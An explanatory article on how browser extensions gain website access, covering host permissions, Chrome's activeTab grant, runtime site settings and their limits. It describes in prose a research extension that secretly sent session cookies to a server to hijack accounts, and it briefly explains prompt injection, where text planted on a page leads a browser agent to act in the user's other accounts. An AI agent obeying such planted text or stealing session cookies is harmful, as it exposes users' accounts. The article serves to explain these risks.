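# Runtime site access and the activeTab permission in browser extensions, and their use as a model for AI agents

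## How browser extensions gain access to websites

A browser extension is a program that changes or adds to what a web browser does. Extensions can block advertisements, fill in passwords or translate pages, for example. Most users get them from a store run by the browser's maker. The largest store, the Chrome Web Store, held nearly 200,000 active extensions in December 2025 (Chaudhry, Dalla Valle and Fass, *Two Heads are Better Than One*, 2026).

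Many browser extensions need access to the websites their users visit. Chrome can grant an extension access at installation to every site its developer listed, and that access lasts until someone removes it. Chrome can also withhold access until the extension is in use, which is called runtime site access. Its narrowest form is the activeTab permission, which gives an extension access to the current tab when the user invokes the extension. Chrome still grants access at installation by default for the sites an extension requires.

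Chrome's design also matters for Microsoft Edge, Opera and Brave, which build on the same open-source project, Chromium. In *Towards Browser Controls to Protect Cookies from Malicious Extensions*, Tyler and De Oliveira Nunes (2024) wrote test extensions for Chrome that ran unchanged in the other three browsers.

### The parts of an extension

An extension is a bundle of files written in HTML, CSS and JavaScript, the same languages used to build web pages. Every extension must include a file called `manifest.json`, which the browser reads first. It lists the extension's name and version, the scripts in the bundle, and the permissions the developer wants. The browser limits the extension to those permissions.

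An extension's main logic runs in a background script, which in current extensions is a service worker. It does not belong to any web page. It starts when an event relevant to the extension occurs, such as a new tab opening, and stops after a period of inactivity. It can use every browser function that the manifest permits. Seetharam, Nabeel and Melicher (2025), in *Malicious GenAI Chrome Extensions*, describe it as the extension's privileged core.

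The browser inserts an extension's content scripts into web pages, where they can read and change the text, forms and layout. These scripts run separately from the page's own scripts and can use only a few of the browser's extension functions. For anything more, they send a message to the extension's service worker. This split is meant to keep a hostile page that takes over a content script from gaining the extension's full powers.

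The user interacts with the extension through a button in the toolbar. Clicking it may open a popup, a small page that exists only while it is visible, or a side panel, which can stay open next to the website. In a translation extension, for example, the user might click the button and pick a language in the popup. A content script would then collect the page's text and pass it to the service worker, which would send it to a translation server. Finally, the content script would write the translation into the page.

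### Origins, match patterns and permissions

Browsers separate websites by origin, the combination of scheme, host name and port in a web address. `https://mail.example.com` and `https://shop.example.com` are different origins because their host names differ, and `http://mail.example.com` is a third because its scheme differs. The same-origin policy prevents a script running in one origin from reading another origin's pages or data unless the other site allows it. Without this rule, a page open in one tab could read the mail open in another.

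A translation extension has to read pages that belong to other people, so it would be useless if it strictly obeyed the same-origin policy. Browsers therefore let extensions bypass the policy. *Work-in-Progress* (Pantelaios and Kapravelos, 2024) lists this ability among the powers that make extensions a concern for security researchers. The extent of the bypass depends mostly on the extension's host permissions.

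A host permission lets an extension work with the pages and data of particular sites. Developers write it as a match pattern, a string with wildcards that names a group of addresses. For example, `https://*.example.com/*` covers `example.com` and all its subdomains over an encrypted connection. Both `*://*/*` and the special string `<all_urls>` cover every ordinary web page. A developer can also add a path, such as `/maps`, but Chromium ignores the path in host permissions and gives the extension access to the whole host, according to *Extension Permissions*, a Chromium document on the browser's internals.

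API permissions are a separate matter. An API is a set of functions that the browser offers to programs, and an API permission is a word in the manifest that switches one of these sets on: `storage` for saving data, `cookies` for handling cookies, and so on. A simple manifest for the translation extension might look like this:

```json
{
  "manifest_version": 3,
  "name": "Page Translator",
  "version": "1.0",
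  "permissions": ["storage", "scripting"],
  "host_permissions": ["https://*.example.com/*"],
  "optional_host_permissions": ["https://*/*"]
}
```

The two kinds of permission often work as a pair. `scripting` lets the extension insert code into pages, but only into pages it has access to, and `cookies` likewise yields only the cookies of permitted hosts. Chrome for Developers, Google's documentation site, gives a list of what host permissions make possible, some of it in combination with an API permission:

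- sending requests to the site from the service worker or the extension's own pages
- reading the address, title and icon of a tab
- inserting a content script while the extension is running
- watching and controlling network requests
- reading and changing cookies
- redirecting requests and modifying the headers that travel with them

An extension can also gain access to sites that aren't listed under `host_permissions`, so that list alone can understate its reach. A developer can declare a content script in the manifest with its own match patterns, and Chrome will run it on the matching sites, which Chromium's document calls scriptable hosts. This access only allows the script to run, but the user sees the same sort of warning as for a host permission, because both let the extension read and change data on the site. The `debugger` permission needs no host permission either. According to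 Chrome for Developers' *Permissions list*, it triggers the warning "Read and change all your data on all websites" by itself.

### What access means in a logged-in browser

People stay logged in to their mail, their bank and their employer's systems, and an extension runs in that same browser. A content script on a mail page can read the same messages as the account's owner without needing a password, because the user has already logged in.

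After a login, a website typically stores a session cookie, a value that the browser sends back with each request so that the user doesn't have to log in again. Anyone who has this value can often impersonate the user, even from outside the user's browser. Websites can mark a cookie `HttpOnly`, which hides it from scripts in the page, or `Secure`, which keeps it off unencrypted connections. An extension with the right permissions can still read the cookie, either through the browser's own functions or from the request before the browser encrypts it.

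One of Tyler and De Oliveira Nunes's test extensions looked like a tool for viewing and editing cookies, but it secretly sent cookies from Google, Amazon, Facebook and other sites to a server. The researchers then loaded the stolen cookies into a fresh copy of Firefox and got into the corresponding test accounts without entering any credentials. The attack used the `cookies` permission and access to the sites, both of which a real cookie manager would also need, and it required no flaw in the browser.

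### The install prompt and standing access

When a user adds an extension, Chrome shows a prompt with a warning for each serious capability the extension requires. The user can add the extension or cancel, but can't use the prompt to choose which sites the extension can access. For example, they can't allow a translator on news sites but block it on their bank's site.

Chrome also keeps the list of warnings short. Some permissions, such as `storage`, produce no warning because Chromium's developers consider them fairly harmless. Chrome also leaves out warnings that a broader one covers, so an extension that requests all of `google.com` and also `maps.google.com` produces only the warning about `google.com`. But a translator and a cookie thief that both require access to every site can produce much the same warning, and it describes what an extension is able to do, which tells the user little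 about what it will do.

Once the user accepts, Chromium records the permissions and restores them whenever it loads the extension. This standing access continues whether or not the user still uses the extension. However, the extension cannot run in incognito windows or on files from the user's disk until the user turns that on in the extension's details page. The user can also reduce site access later in Chrome's settings.

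Extensions also update themselves in the background, and each new version keeps the access that the user granted to the old one. If an update adds permissions that bring a new warning, Chrome disables the extension until the user approves. If the added permissions bring no new warning, Chrome installs the update without asking. Chromium's document gives an example in which version 1 of an extension has a permission, version 2 drops it and version 3 requests it again. Chromium doesn't ask users who installed version 1 to approve the permission again, because it still counts it as granted.

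An attacker can gain access to websites by acquiring an extension that people already trust. Seetharam and colleagues cite The Great Suspender, a popular extension whose developer sold it. The new owner then shipped malicious code in an update to people who had chosen to install the extension when the original developer ran it.

### What Manifest V3 changed

Google has since replaced Manifest V2, the format in which developers wrote extensions, with Manifest V3. The Chrome Web Store began phasing out support for V2 in 2022. Most of the changes concern code. An extension may no longer download JavaScript from a server and run it, so store reviewers can at least see all the code that will run. Service workers replaced background pages that could run permanently. Ordinary extensions in Chrome also can no longer hold up a network request while their own code decides what to do with it; they now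 give the browser a set of rules in advance.

The change to site access was smaller. In Manifest V2, developers listed match patterns and API names together under `permissions`. Manifest V3 moves the patterns to a separate key, `host_permissions`, and has another key, `optional_host_permissions`, for sites the extension doesn't need at first. Chrome for Developers' *Update the manifest* shows an extension that requires access to one blogging site and makes the rest of the web optional. Users grant access to the optional sites later, when the extension requests it. But developers choose which key to use, and they can still require access to every site from the start by putting `*://*/*` under `host_permissions`.

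Google had planned to go further. *A question about &lt;all_urls&gt; host permissions in MV3* (Howard, 2020), posted to a mailing list for extension developers in November 2020, quoted the design document for Manifest V3. According to that document, extensions would be unable to request `<all_urls>`, and access in the style of activeTab would become the default. Google's extensions team also told a developer conference that year that a future release would stop granting declared hosts at installation by default. This had not happened by May 2023, when Vincent (2023), in *Default host permission grants during installation*, asked the Chrome team on the same list about the status of the plan. He noted that the team's latest talk mentioned only exploring easier ways for users to toggle host permissions at install. In Chrome's documentation, runtime grants are still only for optional permissions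 and hosts.

Manifest V3 has a mixed effect on malicious extensions. Pantelaios and Kapravelos used an automatic tool to convert 517 known malicious extensions from the old format to Manifest V3. Of these, 154 still worked, meaning that they loaded and tried to contact a known malicious address. The number rose to 290, or 56%, after the researchers adjusted how the extensions declared their bundled files. This does not show that Manifest V3 stops the other 44%, because some of those failures may come from the converter, which could not handle every extension. The cookie theft that Tyler and De Oliveira Nunes demonstrated worked in both formats.

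### How common broad access is

In March 2024, the same two researchers collected the manifests of 119,152 Chrome extensions and 37,631 Firefox extensions and searched them for patterns that cover all websites, or all sites that use one URL scheme. They found such a pattern in 35.2% of all the extensions and 35.3% of the Chrome ones.

That figure is probably too high as a measure of standing access, because the researchers looked for the patterns anywhere in the manifest. A pattern under an optional key grants no access at installation. In Manifest V3, a pattern can also appear in an entry that controls which websites may load the extension's files, and there it gives the extension no access to those websites.

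A newer count is much lower. Extension Auditor's *We Scanned 534,000 Chrome Extensions. Here's What We Found*, an undated page that was online in August 2026, reports that 25,709 of 226,550 active extensions, or 11.3%, request access to all URLs. Extension Auditor sells monitoring of extensions and does not explain how it counted. If it counted host permissions but not content scripts, that could explain much of the gap. Its total is also larger than the nearly 200,000 active extensions that Chaudhry and colleagues give for December 2025. The two percentages are therefore not good evidence that the share fell from a third to a ninth in two years.

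Narrower powers are less common. Tyler and De Oliveira Nunes found the `cookies` permission in 5% of extensions, and over half of those could access every site's cookies. *Passwords and FIDO2 Are Meant To Be Secret* (2025) reports that 4,169 of 101,414 Chrome extensions from August and September 2022, about 4%, could read the body of any web request, which contains the password when a user logs in. Nineteen of those 4,169 extensions had at least 500,000 users each.

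The mix of extensions installed at companies differs from the mix in a store. LayerX's *Enterprise Browser Extension Security Report 2026* (2026) uses data from more than a million devices at the security firm's customers and puts 34.6% of extensions in its "critical" class of permissions. LayerX does not define the class, so this figure cannot be meaningfully compared with the 35.2%. LayerX also found that about one in six enterprise users has at least one AI extension, and that some of these extensions can act for the user.

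A browser agent is an AI system that reads pages, clicks, types and navigates in a browser for a user. Browser agents are exposed to prompt injection, in which the system wrongly treats text in a page or another source as instructions. If an agent has standing access to every site, a sentence that an attacker plants on one page can lead it to act in the user's accounts on other sites.

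## How the activeTab permission works

A developer can declare `activeTab` in the manifest instead of listing sites. The extension then can't read any page until the user invokes it, and it loses access when the tab moves to another site or closes. Chrome shows no warning for `activeTab` in the install prompt.

Chrome for Developers explains the purpose of `activeTab` with the example of a web clipper, an extension that saves pages. A clipper needs access to a page only when the user clicks its button or picks its menu item. Without `activeTab`, it would have to request permanent access to every website so that it could save whichever page the user chose.

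### The gestures that start a grant

Chrome accepts four user gestures:

- clicking the extension's toolbar button, which Chrome's documentation calls its action
- choosing an item that the extension added to the context menu
- pressing a keyboard shortcut that the extension registered
- accepting a suggestion from the extension in the address bar

Firefox has nearly the same list, although it has counted address-bar suggestions only since version 142. A click inside an ordinary web page doesn't count as invoking the extension. Otherwise, an extension could take any click on a page as permission. MDN's *User actions*, part of Mozilla's developer documentation, gives the example of a button on a web page, where a content script listens for clicks on the button and can send the extension a message when one occurs.

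If the toolbar button opens a popup, clicking the button is enough to give the extension access to the tab. Chromium's code grants access and then shows the popup, so the user doesn't have to press anything inside it. When Firefox's developers discussed letting extensions open their own popups, this was a problem because an extension could have gained access to a page without the user doing anything. A proposed fix in Mozilla's bug tracker was to require a user action first.

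The browser also has to grant access to the right tab. A user can right-click a tab in the background and choose an extension's menu item. Before version 63, Firefox gave the extension access to the tab on screen instead of the one the user had right-clicked, according to Mozilla's *activeTab permission not granted for tab on which the contextmenu is used*.

### What the extension receives

After a gesture, Chromium looks up the address of the tab's page and checks whether the extension declared `activeTab`. If it did, Chromium adds the page's origin to a set of permissions for that tab. Chromium does the same for an extension that requires access to the site but has had it withheld, which is how Chrome's "on click" setting works. The gesture doesn't override the separate setting that controls access to files on the user's disk.

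While the grant lasts, the extension can:

- insert scripts and style sheets into the page, if it also declares `scripting`
- read the tab's address, title and icon
- watch network requests from the tab to the origin of the main frame, meaning the page itself and not other pages embedded in it

An extension with `activeTab` can also take a screenshot of the visible tab. Firefox is more restrictive than Chrome about intercepting network requests. A developer reported to Mozilla that an extension using `activeTab` to do this worked in Chrome but not in Firefox.

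Script injection is the broadest of these powers. The permission does not limit the extension to reading, or to the part of the page the user selected. Chrome for Developers describes `activeTab` as essentially a temporary host permission.

The grant also covers more than the page on screen, because Chromium adds the page's origin to the list of sites from which the extension's own pages and service worker can request data. If a user invokes an extension on one email, the extension can probably also request other pages from the same webmail site, such as the inbox.

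### When access ends

Since Chrome 72, activeTab access has lasted until the user navigates to a different origin, according to a note in an older version of the Chrome for Developers page. The current page is inconsistent about this. It says that access ends when the user "navigates away or closes the tab", which describes the earlier rule, but in its example an extension invoked on `https://example.com` still has access after the user moves to `https://example.com/foo`.

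Chromium's source code confirms the newer description. When a navigation finishes, the browser clears the grant only if the main frame has loaded a page from another origin. The grant survives reloads, links within the same origin, and navigation inside an embedded frame. Closing the tab or disabling the extension also ends it. The code sets no time limit, so an extension invoked on a mail site keeps its access for as long as the tab stays there.

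Chromium's developers first kept the grant across pages of the same origin only behind an experimental flag, which made extension scripts wait for a user's action before they ran. They wrote in the change's code review description that they hadn't confirmed that keeping the grant was safe. In a comment in a later version of the code, a developer called the flag's feature almost unusable without the longer grant, but doubted that the longer grant was good for `activeTab` in general and suggested that Chrome would probably need some user interface for it first.

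An automated Chromium test from the period in between checks that navigating within the same origin ends access unless Chrome's runtime host permissions feature is on. The longer `activeTab` grant therefore seems to have arrived with the settings for controlling site access. One comment in Chromium's code still describes the old rule, under which even a refresh ended the grant.

An origin doesn't always match what a user thinks of as one site. If the user moves from `https://mail.example.com` to `https://shop.example.com`, the extension loses access even though one company runs both. It also loses access if the user visits a separate login site and comes back. But a webmail service may keep thousands of messages under one origin. If a user invokes a translator on a newsletter and then opens a message from their doctor in the same tab, the translator still has access.

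### A clipping extension from click to revocation

Suppose a clipper declares `activeTab`, `scripting` and `storage`, and no host permissions. The user browses in one tab:

| What the user does | What the clipper can do |
|---|---|
| Opens `https://example.com` | It can't read the page, or even see its address and title. |
| Clicks the clipper's button | It can insert a script, copy the text, save it and send it to the developer's server. |
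| Follows a link to `https://example.com/foo` | The script in the first page stops when that page unloads. The clipper can insert a new script into `/foo` without another click. |
| Moves to `https://example.org` | It can't read the new page, because Chromium has cleared the grant. |
| Returns to `https://example.com/foo` | It needs another click before it can insert a script. |

The clipper still has what it copied. If it saved the text in its own storage, the text stays there, and if it sent the text to a server, Chrome can't delete it.

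Chromium's *Extensions Security FAQ* discusses what remains after a user uninstalls an extension, and much of it also applies to activeTab. Changes to a site's data persist, so a cookie that an extension altered, for example, can affect how the site behaves later.

Injected scripts also keep running until the user leaves or refreshes the page, because Chromium can't remove them. This rarely matters when an `activeTab` grant ends, since moving to another origin normally unloads the page and the script with it. It matters more if the user disables or removes the clipper while the page is open, because the script already in the page keeps running even though the clipper can't inject anything new.

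### Clicks inside a side panel

Many developers want to put tools in a side panel, where some AI agents now run, but `activeTab` works poorly there. Gabriel (2023), in *Possible Bug/Unexpected Behavior with "activetab" Permission and Side Panel View*, described an extension that could take screenshots from its popup. When he moved the same function to a side panel, Chrome blocked it for lack of permission. Jackie Han, another developer in the thread, ran three tests, including one with a button inside the panel, and found that the function worked consistently from the popup but never from the panel.

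Chrome deliberately doesn't grant access to the tab when the user clicks a toolbar button that the developer has set to open the side panel. A comment in Chromium's code gives two reasons. First, the user can also open the extension's panel from the browser's own side panel menu, which grants no access. Second, a panel can stay open while the user changes tabs, so access to one tab shouldn't carry over to another. The comment adds that the developers still have to evaluate whether this is the best approach.

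Oliver Dunk, who works with extension developers at Google, gave a related reason in Gabriel's thread, which was that a panel losing its permissions while still open could confuse people. He was least sure about the inconsistency with popups. Gabriel announced in August 2023 that Chrome had fixed the problem, but developers using Chrome 118 and 119 later that year still got the error.

Mozilla's developers make a different argument, based on what the user means by a click. In Mozilla's *activeTab of permissions is not valid for tabs.executeScript in sidebar_action*, a commenter imagines an extension that keeps a to-do list in Firefox's sidebar. A user who adds milk to a grocery list hasn't asked the extension to read the page next to it. A popup may contain the same list, but the user has just clicked the toolbar button to open it, and the browser treats that click as a request for the extension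 to access the page.

Han proposed a compromise in which a click in the panel would grant access to the current tab and origin, and the browser would revoke that access as soon as the user switched tabs. This would address the Chromium team's concern about access carrying over, but it wouldn't help with the grocery list. The Mozilla commenter considered accepting only genuine clicks on buttons but still expected too many accidental grants.

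The restriction applies to how a grant starts, so a panel can use a grant that began elsewhere. One developer in Gabriel's thread found that the panel worked after he had opened and closed the popup, because the browser grants access to the whole extension. A toolbar click is probably a simpler way to start the grant. According to another Chrome for Developers page, since Chrome 116 an extension can run its own code when the user clicks its toolbar icon, and that code can open the panel. Judging by Chromium's code, the click counts as an ordinary action and grants access.

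### Embedded frames from other sites

A web page can embed another page in a frame. Shops embed payment forms this way, and news sites embed videos and advertisements. The user sees one page, but its parts may come from several origins.

In Chrome, activeTab grants access only to the origin of the top page. Gordon (2024) reports in *Dynamic Insert into iFrame w/ ActiveTab permission* that a click on his extension's menu item let it insert a script into the page, but not into a frame from a different subdomain of the same company. He had expected the click to give the extension access to the whole tab.

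Firefox once let an extension with only `activeTab` use frames to run code on sites that the user hadn't opened. An outside researcher showed this in 2017, and the discussion is in Mozilla's *An extension can XSS any domain with only the ActiveTab permission*, where XSS means running one's own script in another site's page. One Firefox developer answered that access to frames was intentional. Another replied that it made `activeTab` about as dangerous as access to every site, except that the user first had to click, and that Firefox didn't warn users of this at installation. Mozilla treated the behaviour as a security flaw, CVE-2018-5116, and fixed it in Firefox 58.

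After the fix, extensions could still reach frames in the page's original HTML, but not frames that a script had created. Mozilla confirmed this when a developer complained. Firefox couldn't reliably determine whether a script-created frame came from the page or the extension, so it excluded both kinds.

Firefox 105 narrowed activeTab access again for Manifest V3 extensions, to frames that share the top page's origin. Mozilla's *Make activeTab target sameOriginWithTop iframes in MV3* gives two reasons: Chrome and Safari already worked this way, and Firefox's new controls would tell users that a click gives access to the tab's top-level domain.

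Some developers think that excluding frames from other origins misreads what users intend. In Mozilla's *browser.tabs.executeScript(..., {allFrames*, the developer who filed the report argues that a person who clicks an extension means it to work on everything in the tab. An extension that translates a page or searches its text would seem broken if it skipped a frame in the middle. Mozilla's *activeTab does not enable scripting.executeScript to execute in iframe with different origin* gives the argument for the narrow rule, which is that users can see which tab an extension is acting on but can't easily find out where each frame comes from.

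The security argument is stronger, because the 2017 flaw involved frames that the extension itself had created. But under the narrow rule, an extension that needs frames from unpredictable sites has to request access to all sites, which was described in the same Mozilla discussion as far more dangerous than `activeTab`. Gordon eventually made every site an optional host permission and had his extension prompt the user for access to a frame's host when it was needed.

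The developers have also suggested ways to cover frames without giving access to every site. In the discussion of the flaw, one suggested including only frames that were already present when the user clicked. This would exclude most frames made by the extension, but users still wouldn't know whose content they were sharing. Another suggestion was a separate permission called `activeTabAndFrames`. Mozilla has left that report open.

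### Why a click can count as consent

Chromium's FAQ compares invoking an extension to sharing a page with an app on an Android phone. The user picks the page and the recipient in one action, without having to answer a permission prompt. Chrome for Developers adds that an attacker who takes over the extension has to wait for the user to invoke it before getting access to a page.

Richardson (2020), in *Feature Request*, proposed loosening the rule by letting web pages ask the user to run an extension, much as they ask to use the camera. Once the user agreed, the extension would keep its access to that address. The fullest defence of the rule from someone at Google was a response to this proposal.

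Simeon Vincent, then Google's advocate for extension developers, replied that this would turn `activeTab` into persistent access. He wrote that reviewers don't need to examine `activeTab` as closely as broad host permissions because the access is temporary, covers only the current site, and is granted when the user invokes the extension. He stressed that these were his own opinions, not the Chrome team's. He also guessed that requiring a gesture stops extensions from pestering people. A user can close a website that keeps asking for permission, but an extension is part of the browser and is harder to get away from.

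In *User-Driven Access Control* (2012), Roesner, Kohno and colleagues developed a similar idea for operating systems. They argued that people grant install-time permissions out of context and the permissions then last forever, while people who see frequent prompts learn to ignore them. They proposed treating things the user does anyway as permission. A camera app would embed a shutter button controlled by the operating system. Clicking it would take one photo and hand it to the app, which would otherwise have no access to the camera.

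This only works if the user actually clicked the button and could see it. In the researchers' prototype, an app can't generate clicks or draw over the button. The button becomes active only after it has been fully visible in the same place for at least 200 milliseconds, so an app can't suddenly place it where the user is about to click. By default, only the outermost app can embed these buttons, because the researchers assumed that users are more aware of it than of the apps nested inside. The rule that `activeTab` excludes frames from other origins rests on much the same assumption.

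Roesner and colleagues also asked 186 people about Android apps that used the camera, location or text messages. On average, most believed that an app could not use these before they pressed the relevant button, and that it should not be able to. They were less concerned about location. The sample was unrepresentative, since 154 of the participants were men, but the result supports the view that people connect access with their own actions. The approach would also suit most uses of such resources. Of 143 uses in 100 popular Android apps, 62% needed only brief access in direct response to a user's action.

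`activeTab` is a looser version of this idea. The operating system controls how the shutter button looks, so the user can tell what pressing it will do. In Chrome, the extension's developer chooses the icon, and clicking it might mean "save this page" or "show me my shopping list". Pressing the shutter button also gives the camera app only a single photo, whereas clicking the icon gives the extension access to the site until the tab leaves it.

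A person who clicks an extension wants to use it but may not understand what it can read. If someone opens a calculator extension while looking at their bank account, and the extension declares `activeTab` and `scripting`, it can read the balance and the list of payments, even though the install prompt never mentioned this. In the discussion of Firefox's frame flaw, a Mozilla engineer said the missing warning seemed deceptive, though he guessed that Chrome's developers took the click as a sign of intent.

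The 2012 research doesn't answer this objection. Its surveys covered when an app could use a resource, and the researchers explicitly excluded the question of what data an app receives. They also acknowledged that a malicious app could trick people into clicking, for instance by using location buttons as the circles in a game of tic-tac-toe.

The objection is weaker for a clipper or a translator, because anyone who uses one must expect it to read the page, though they may not expect it to read the next one. *User Interactions and Permission Use on Android*, a later study that cites Roesner and colleagues, suggests that separate permission dialogs may be unnecessary for resources that apps use mostly in response to the user. It recommends separate authorization for background use. A clipper that reads `example.com/foo` without a second click is closer to background use, and its only authorization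 is a click on the previous page.

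## Chrome's settings for which sites an extension can reach

A developer who declares `activeTab` chooses to make the extension wait for the user. Since Chrome 70, released in October 2018, users have been able to put a similar limit on extensions whose developers asked for standing access. Users can set each extension to run on click, on specific sites or on all sites.

Google wrote on the Chromium Blog that it added the settings because host permissions had led to a lot of misuse, both malicious and unintentional. Extensions that people already had kept their access unless the user restricted it.

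### The three settings

Chrome Story's *How to Control Which Sites Chrome Extensions Access* describes two ways to change the setting in desktop Chrome. The user can right-click the extension's icon, point to "This can read and change site data" and pick an option. The user can also open `chrome://extensions`, click "Details" under the extension and find the site access heading. The right-click menu is quicker, but it can only add the site on screen. On the details page, the user can type in a list of sites. Exame's *A extensão do Chrome precisa ler todos os sites* (2026) explains how to remove added sites.

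| Setting | Access without a click | What a click adds |
|---|---|---|
| On click | None | The current site, if the extension requested it |
| On specific sites | The sites on the user's list | Any other site that the extension requested |
| On all sites | Every site that the extension requested | Nothing more |

"On all sites" is a slightly misleading name, because with this setting, an extension whose manifest lists only one shop's site can access only that site.

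Google's *User controls for host permissions*, a guide for developers, explains that an extension set to "on click" behaves essentially as if it used `activeTab`. When the user clicks the extension, it gets temporary access to the current site. Until then, Chrome marks the extension's icon to show that it is requesting access to the page.

The "on click" setting differs from `activeTab` in two ways. First, it covers only sites that the extension requested. If a price-comparison extension lists three shops and the user clicks it on a newspaper's site, the extension gets no access, whereas one with `activeTab` would get access to the newspaper. Second, an extension with `activeTab` has to insert its script after the click, while an extension written for standing access usually declares its content scripts in the manifest, and Chrome doesn't run them until the user grants access.

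The "on specific sites" setting combines standing access with temporary grants. If a user reads a French newspaper every day and adds it to a translation extension's list, the extension works there automatically. On every other site it requested, it behaves as if the user had chosen "on click", so the user can still translate an occasional Spanish page without adding that site to the list.

Exame and Chrome Story both recommend "on click" as the safest choice for most extensions. It suits a tool that people use now and then, such as a web clipper. It doesn't suit an ad blocker, which has to act on every page before the ads load and which people don't want to click each time.

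The settings only control access to sites. Exame, citing Chrome's support page, notes that an extension that routes the browser's traffic through a VPN or proxy server can keep doing so whatever the user chooses. The company running the server can then see where the requests go. The settings also may not restrict an extension with the `debugger` permission, since that permission doesn't depend on host permissions.

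### How Chromium calculates an extension's access

Chromium's document on extension permissions describes how the browser works out what an extension can access. The calculation uses these sets of permissions:

- Required permissions are the ones that the manifest lists as necessary from the start.
- Optional permissions are the ones that the manifest lists for the extension to request later.
- Active permissions are the ones that Chromium has on record as currently belonging to the extension.
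- Runtime-granted permissions are the ones that the user has given after installation, either through the site settings or by agreeing to a request from the extension.

The document gives the calculation in two steps, which combine into one line:

```
current permissions = active ∩ (required ∪ optional) ∩ runtime-granted
```

The symbol ∪ combines two sets, and ∩ keeps only what they share. An extension can therefore use a permission only if it is recorded as active, the manifest requests it, and the user has granted it at runtime. Withheld permissions are those the manifest requires but the user's settings block.

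For example, suppose an extension requires access to `mail.example.com` and `news.example.org`, and lists `maps.example.net` as optional. The user accepts the install prompt, so the two required sites are active. Later, the user switches the extension to "on specific sites" and lists only the news site:

```
active            = {mail, news}
required/optional = {mail, news, maps}
runtime-granted   = {news}
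current           = {news}
withheld          = {mail}
```

The maps site is neither current nor withheld, because the extension hasn't yet asked the user for it. If the user chose "on click" instead, the runtime-granted set would be empty and the extension would have no default access to any of these sites. When the user chooses "on all sites", Chromium withholds nothing, so the last part of the formula has no effect.

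The formula covers only access to sites, so an extension set to "on click" keeps API permissions such as `storage`. It also leaves out the temporary access that follows a click, which Chromium attaches to the tab and never saves with the other permissions.

Chromium also keeps a record of every permission the user has granted and not revoked, which it uses to decide whether an update needs the user's approval. The developers chose to store runtime grants separately so that they could experiment with the site settings without affecting extensions when the feature was off.

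The last part of the formula also limits what an extension can gain from an update. If a developer sells an extension and the new owner adds more sites to the manifest, the extension doesn't automatically get access to those sites in the browser of someone who chose "on specific sites". It would still have access to the sites already on that person's list, and to any other requested site where the person clicks the extension.

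### When the request and the grant only partly overlap

An extension and its user may describe access differently. Chromium's document works through a case in which an extension requests `*://google.com/maps` and the user grants `https://*.google.com/*`. Neither pattern contains the other, as a comparison of their parts shows:

| Part of the address | The extension requests | The user grants | The extension receives |
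|---|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `http` or `https` | `https` | `https` |
| Host | `google.com` | `google.com` and its subdomains | `google.com` |
| Path | `/maps` | Any path | `/maps` |

Chromium gives the extension access only to the overlap between what the extension requested and what the user granted, which here is `https://google.com/maps`. This excludes the unencrypted pages in the extension's request, which the user hadn't approved, and `mail.google.com`, which the user's grant covered but the extension hadn't requested.

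Chromium ignores paths in host permissions, so a permission for a single path on `https://google.com` would cover the whole origin. Chromium does apply paths for content scripts declared in the manifest, because their patterns only determine where the scripts run.

Chromium deliberately lets users grant more than an extension requested. This keeps the controls simple, because the user can allow a whole site without working out the exact pattern. If the extension later requests another part of the same site, Chromium grants it automatically. A user who allowed `google.com` for a map might not expect this, but someone who adds a site to a list probably thinks they are allowing the whole site anyway.

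### What stops working when Chrome withholds access

Many developers assume that their extension will have access to every site it needs. When a user restricts that access, some of the extension's functions don't run until the user clicks the extension, and others fail.

A developer can set a content script to run as the page starts to load, just after the browser has built the page, or once the page has mostly finished loading. If the user grants access to a page that is already open, a script of the last kind can run immediately. For the other two kinds, Chrome asks the user to refresh the page because the moment when they should run has passed. For example, an ad blocker that hides advertisements before they appear would need a refresh, but a translator could probably start right away.

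The same applies to extensions that watch or change network requests. The page has already sent most of its requests by the time the user grants access, so Chrome again asks the user to refresh the page.

A running extension can also ask Chrome to insert a script. If the extension lacks access to the site, Chrome marks the extension's icon and, according to Google's guide, replies only if the user grants access. If the developer didn't plan for this, the extension could keep waiting.

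Cookies and background requests are harder to handle because an extension's service worker may try to read a site's cookies or request its data when no tab has the site open. Chrome then has no tab in which to show that the extension needs access, so it doesn't mark the icon. The attempt fails as if the manifest had never listed the site. The extension's code receives an error, but the user sees nothing unless the developer wrote a message for it.

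An extension might check a webmail account every few minutes and show the number of unread messages on its icon. If the user sets its site access to "on click", the checks fail. Unless the developer has made the extension show a warning when this happens, the icon might show zero, and the user would think there was no new mail.

Developers can avoid this by using a Chrome function to check whether the extension has access before it uses that access. For cookies and background requests, Google recommends making the site an optional permission and asking for it when the user turns on the feature that needs it, so that the developer can explain the request in context.

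These failures are a drawback of limiting access, and they mostly affect people who try to be careful. Someone who restricts an extension and then finds it broken may not realize the restriction caused the problem, and may go back to "on all sites" for every extension.

### The redesigned extensions menu

The settings don't help people who never find them. Google has been working for several years on a new version of the menu that opens from the puzzle-piece button in Chrome's toolbar. The existing menu already grouped extensions by how much data they could access on the current tab, according to Google's *Announcement* of that menu.

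The redesign was available behind an experimental flag by July 2023, when Dwivedi asked other developers what they thought of it in *Chrome's Redesigned Extension Toolbar Menu* (2023). Google previewed it at its developer conference in May 2024, and in November announced tests with a small percentage of users of Canary, Chrome's experimental version.

Google's *Prepare your extension as we begin testing a new extensions menu* (2024) describes a menu that shows more clearly which extensions can run on the current page and lets users change an extension's access. Users can also stop all extensions from running on a particular site. If a user has withheld access to a site, the extension can request it, and an "Allow" message appears next to the puzzle-piece icon.

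Google repeatedly told developers that the menu would only make existing controls easier to find and would not change the default of full access at installation. Its representatives took the same position at a March 2025 meeting of browser makers and extension developers, according to notes published by the WebExtensions Community Group (WECG, 2025).

Many developers disliked the design. In *The new extensions menu is unwieldy due to overabundance of extraneous info*, woxxom (2025) complained that a line about site access now appeared under every extension's name, which made the names harder to read and the list longer. He thought almost nobody needs this information when they open the menu. Another developer in the thread couldn't tell whether the switch next to each extension turned it off everywhere or only on the current site.

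Oliver Dunk of Google replied that making site access more visible was intentional. He wrote that many users give extensions broad access without fully understanding what that means, and the team hoped to change their behaviour over time. Some of the choices came from user studies. For example, the team had dropped the groups because people were often confused about why an extension was in one group and not another.

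It is hard to judge who is right about what users want. Woxxom claimed that people need to adjust site access 0.001% of the time they use extensions, but gave no data. He also fairly pointed out that Google hadn't published the methods or results of its studies. Dunk acknowledged that real use could differ from the studies and said this was why the team was rolling the menu out cautiously.

Alexei Miagkov, another developer in the thread, argued that the Chrome Web Store still promotes extensions that steal browsing data, and that it's absurd to expect users to protect themselves with partial limits on extensions they can't trust. He expected people to dismiss unwanted settings as quickly as possible and to allow or block things by accident.

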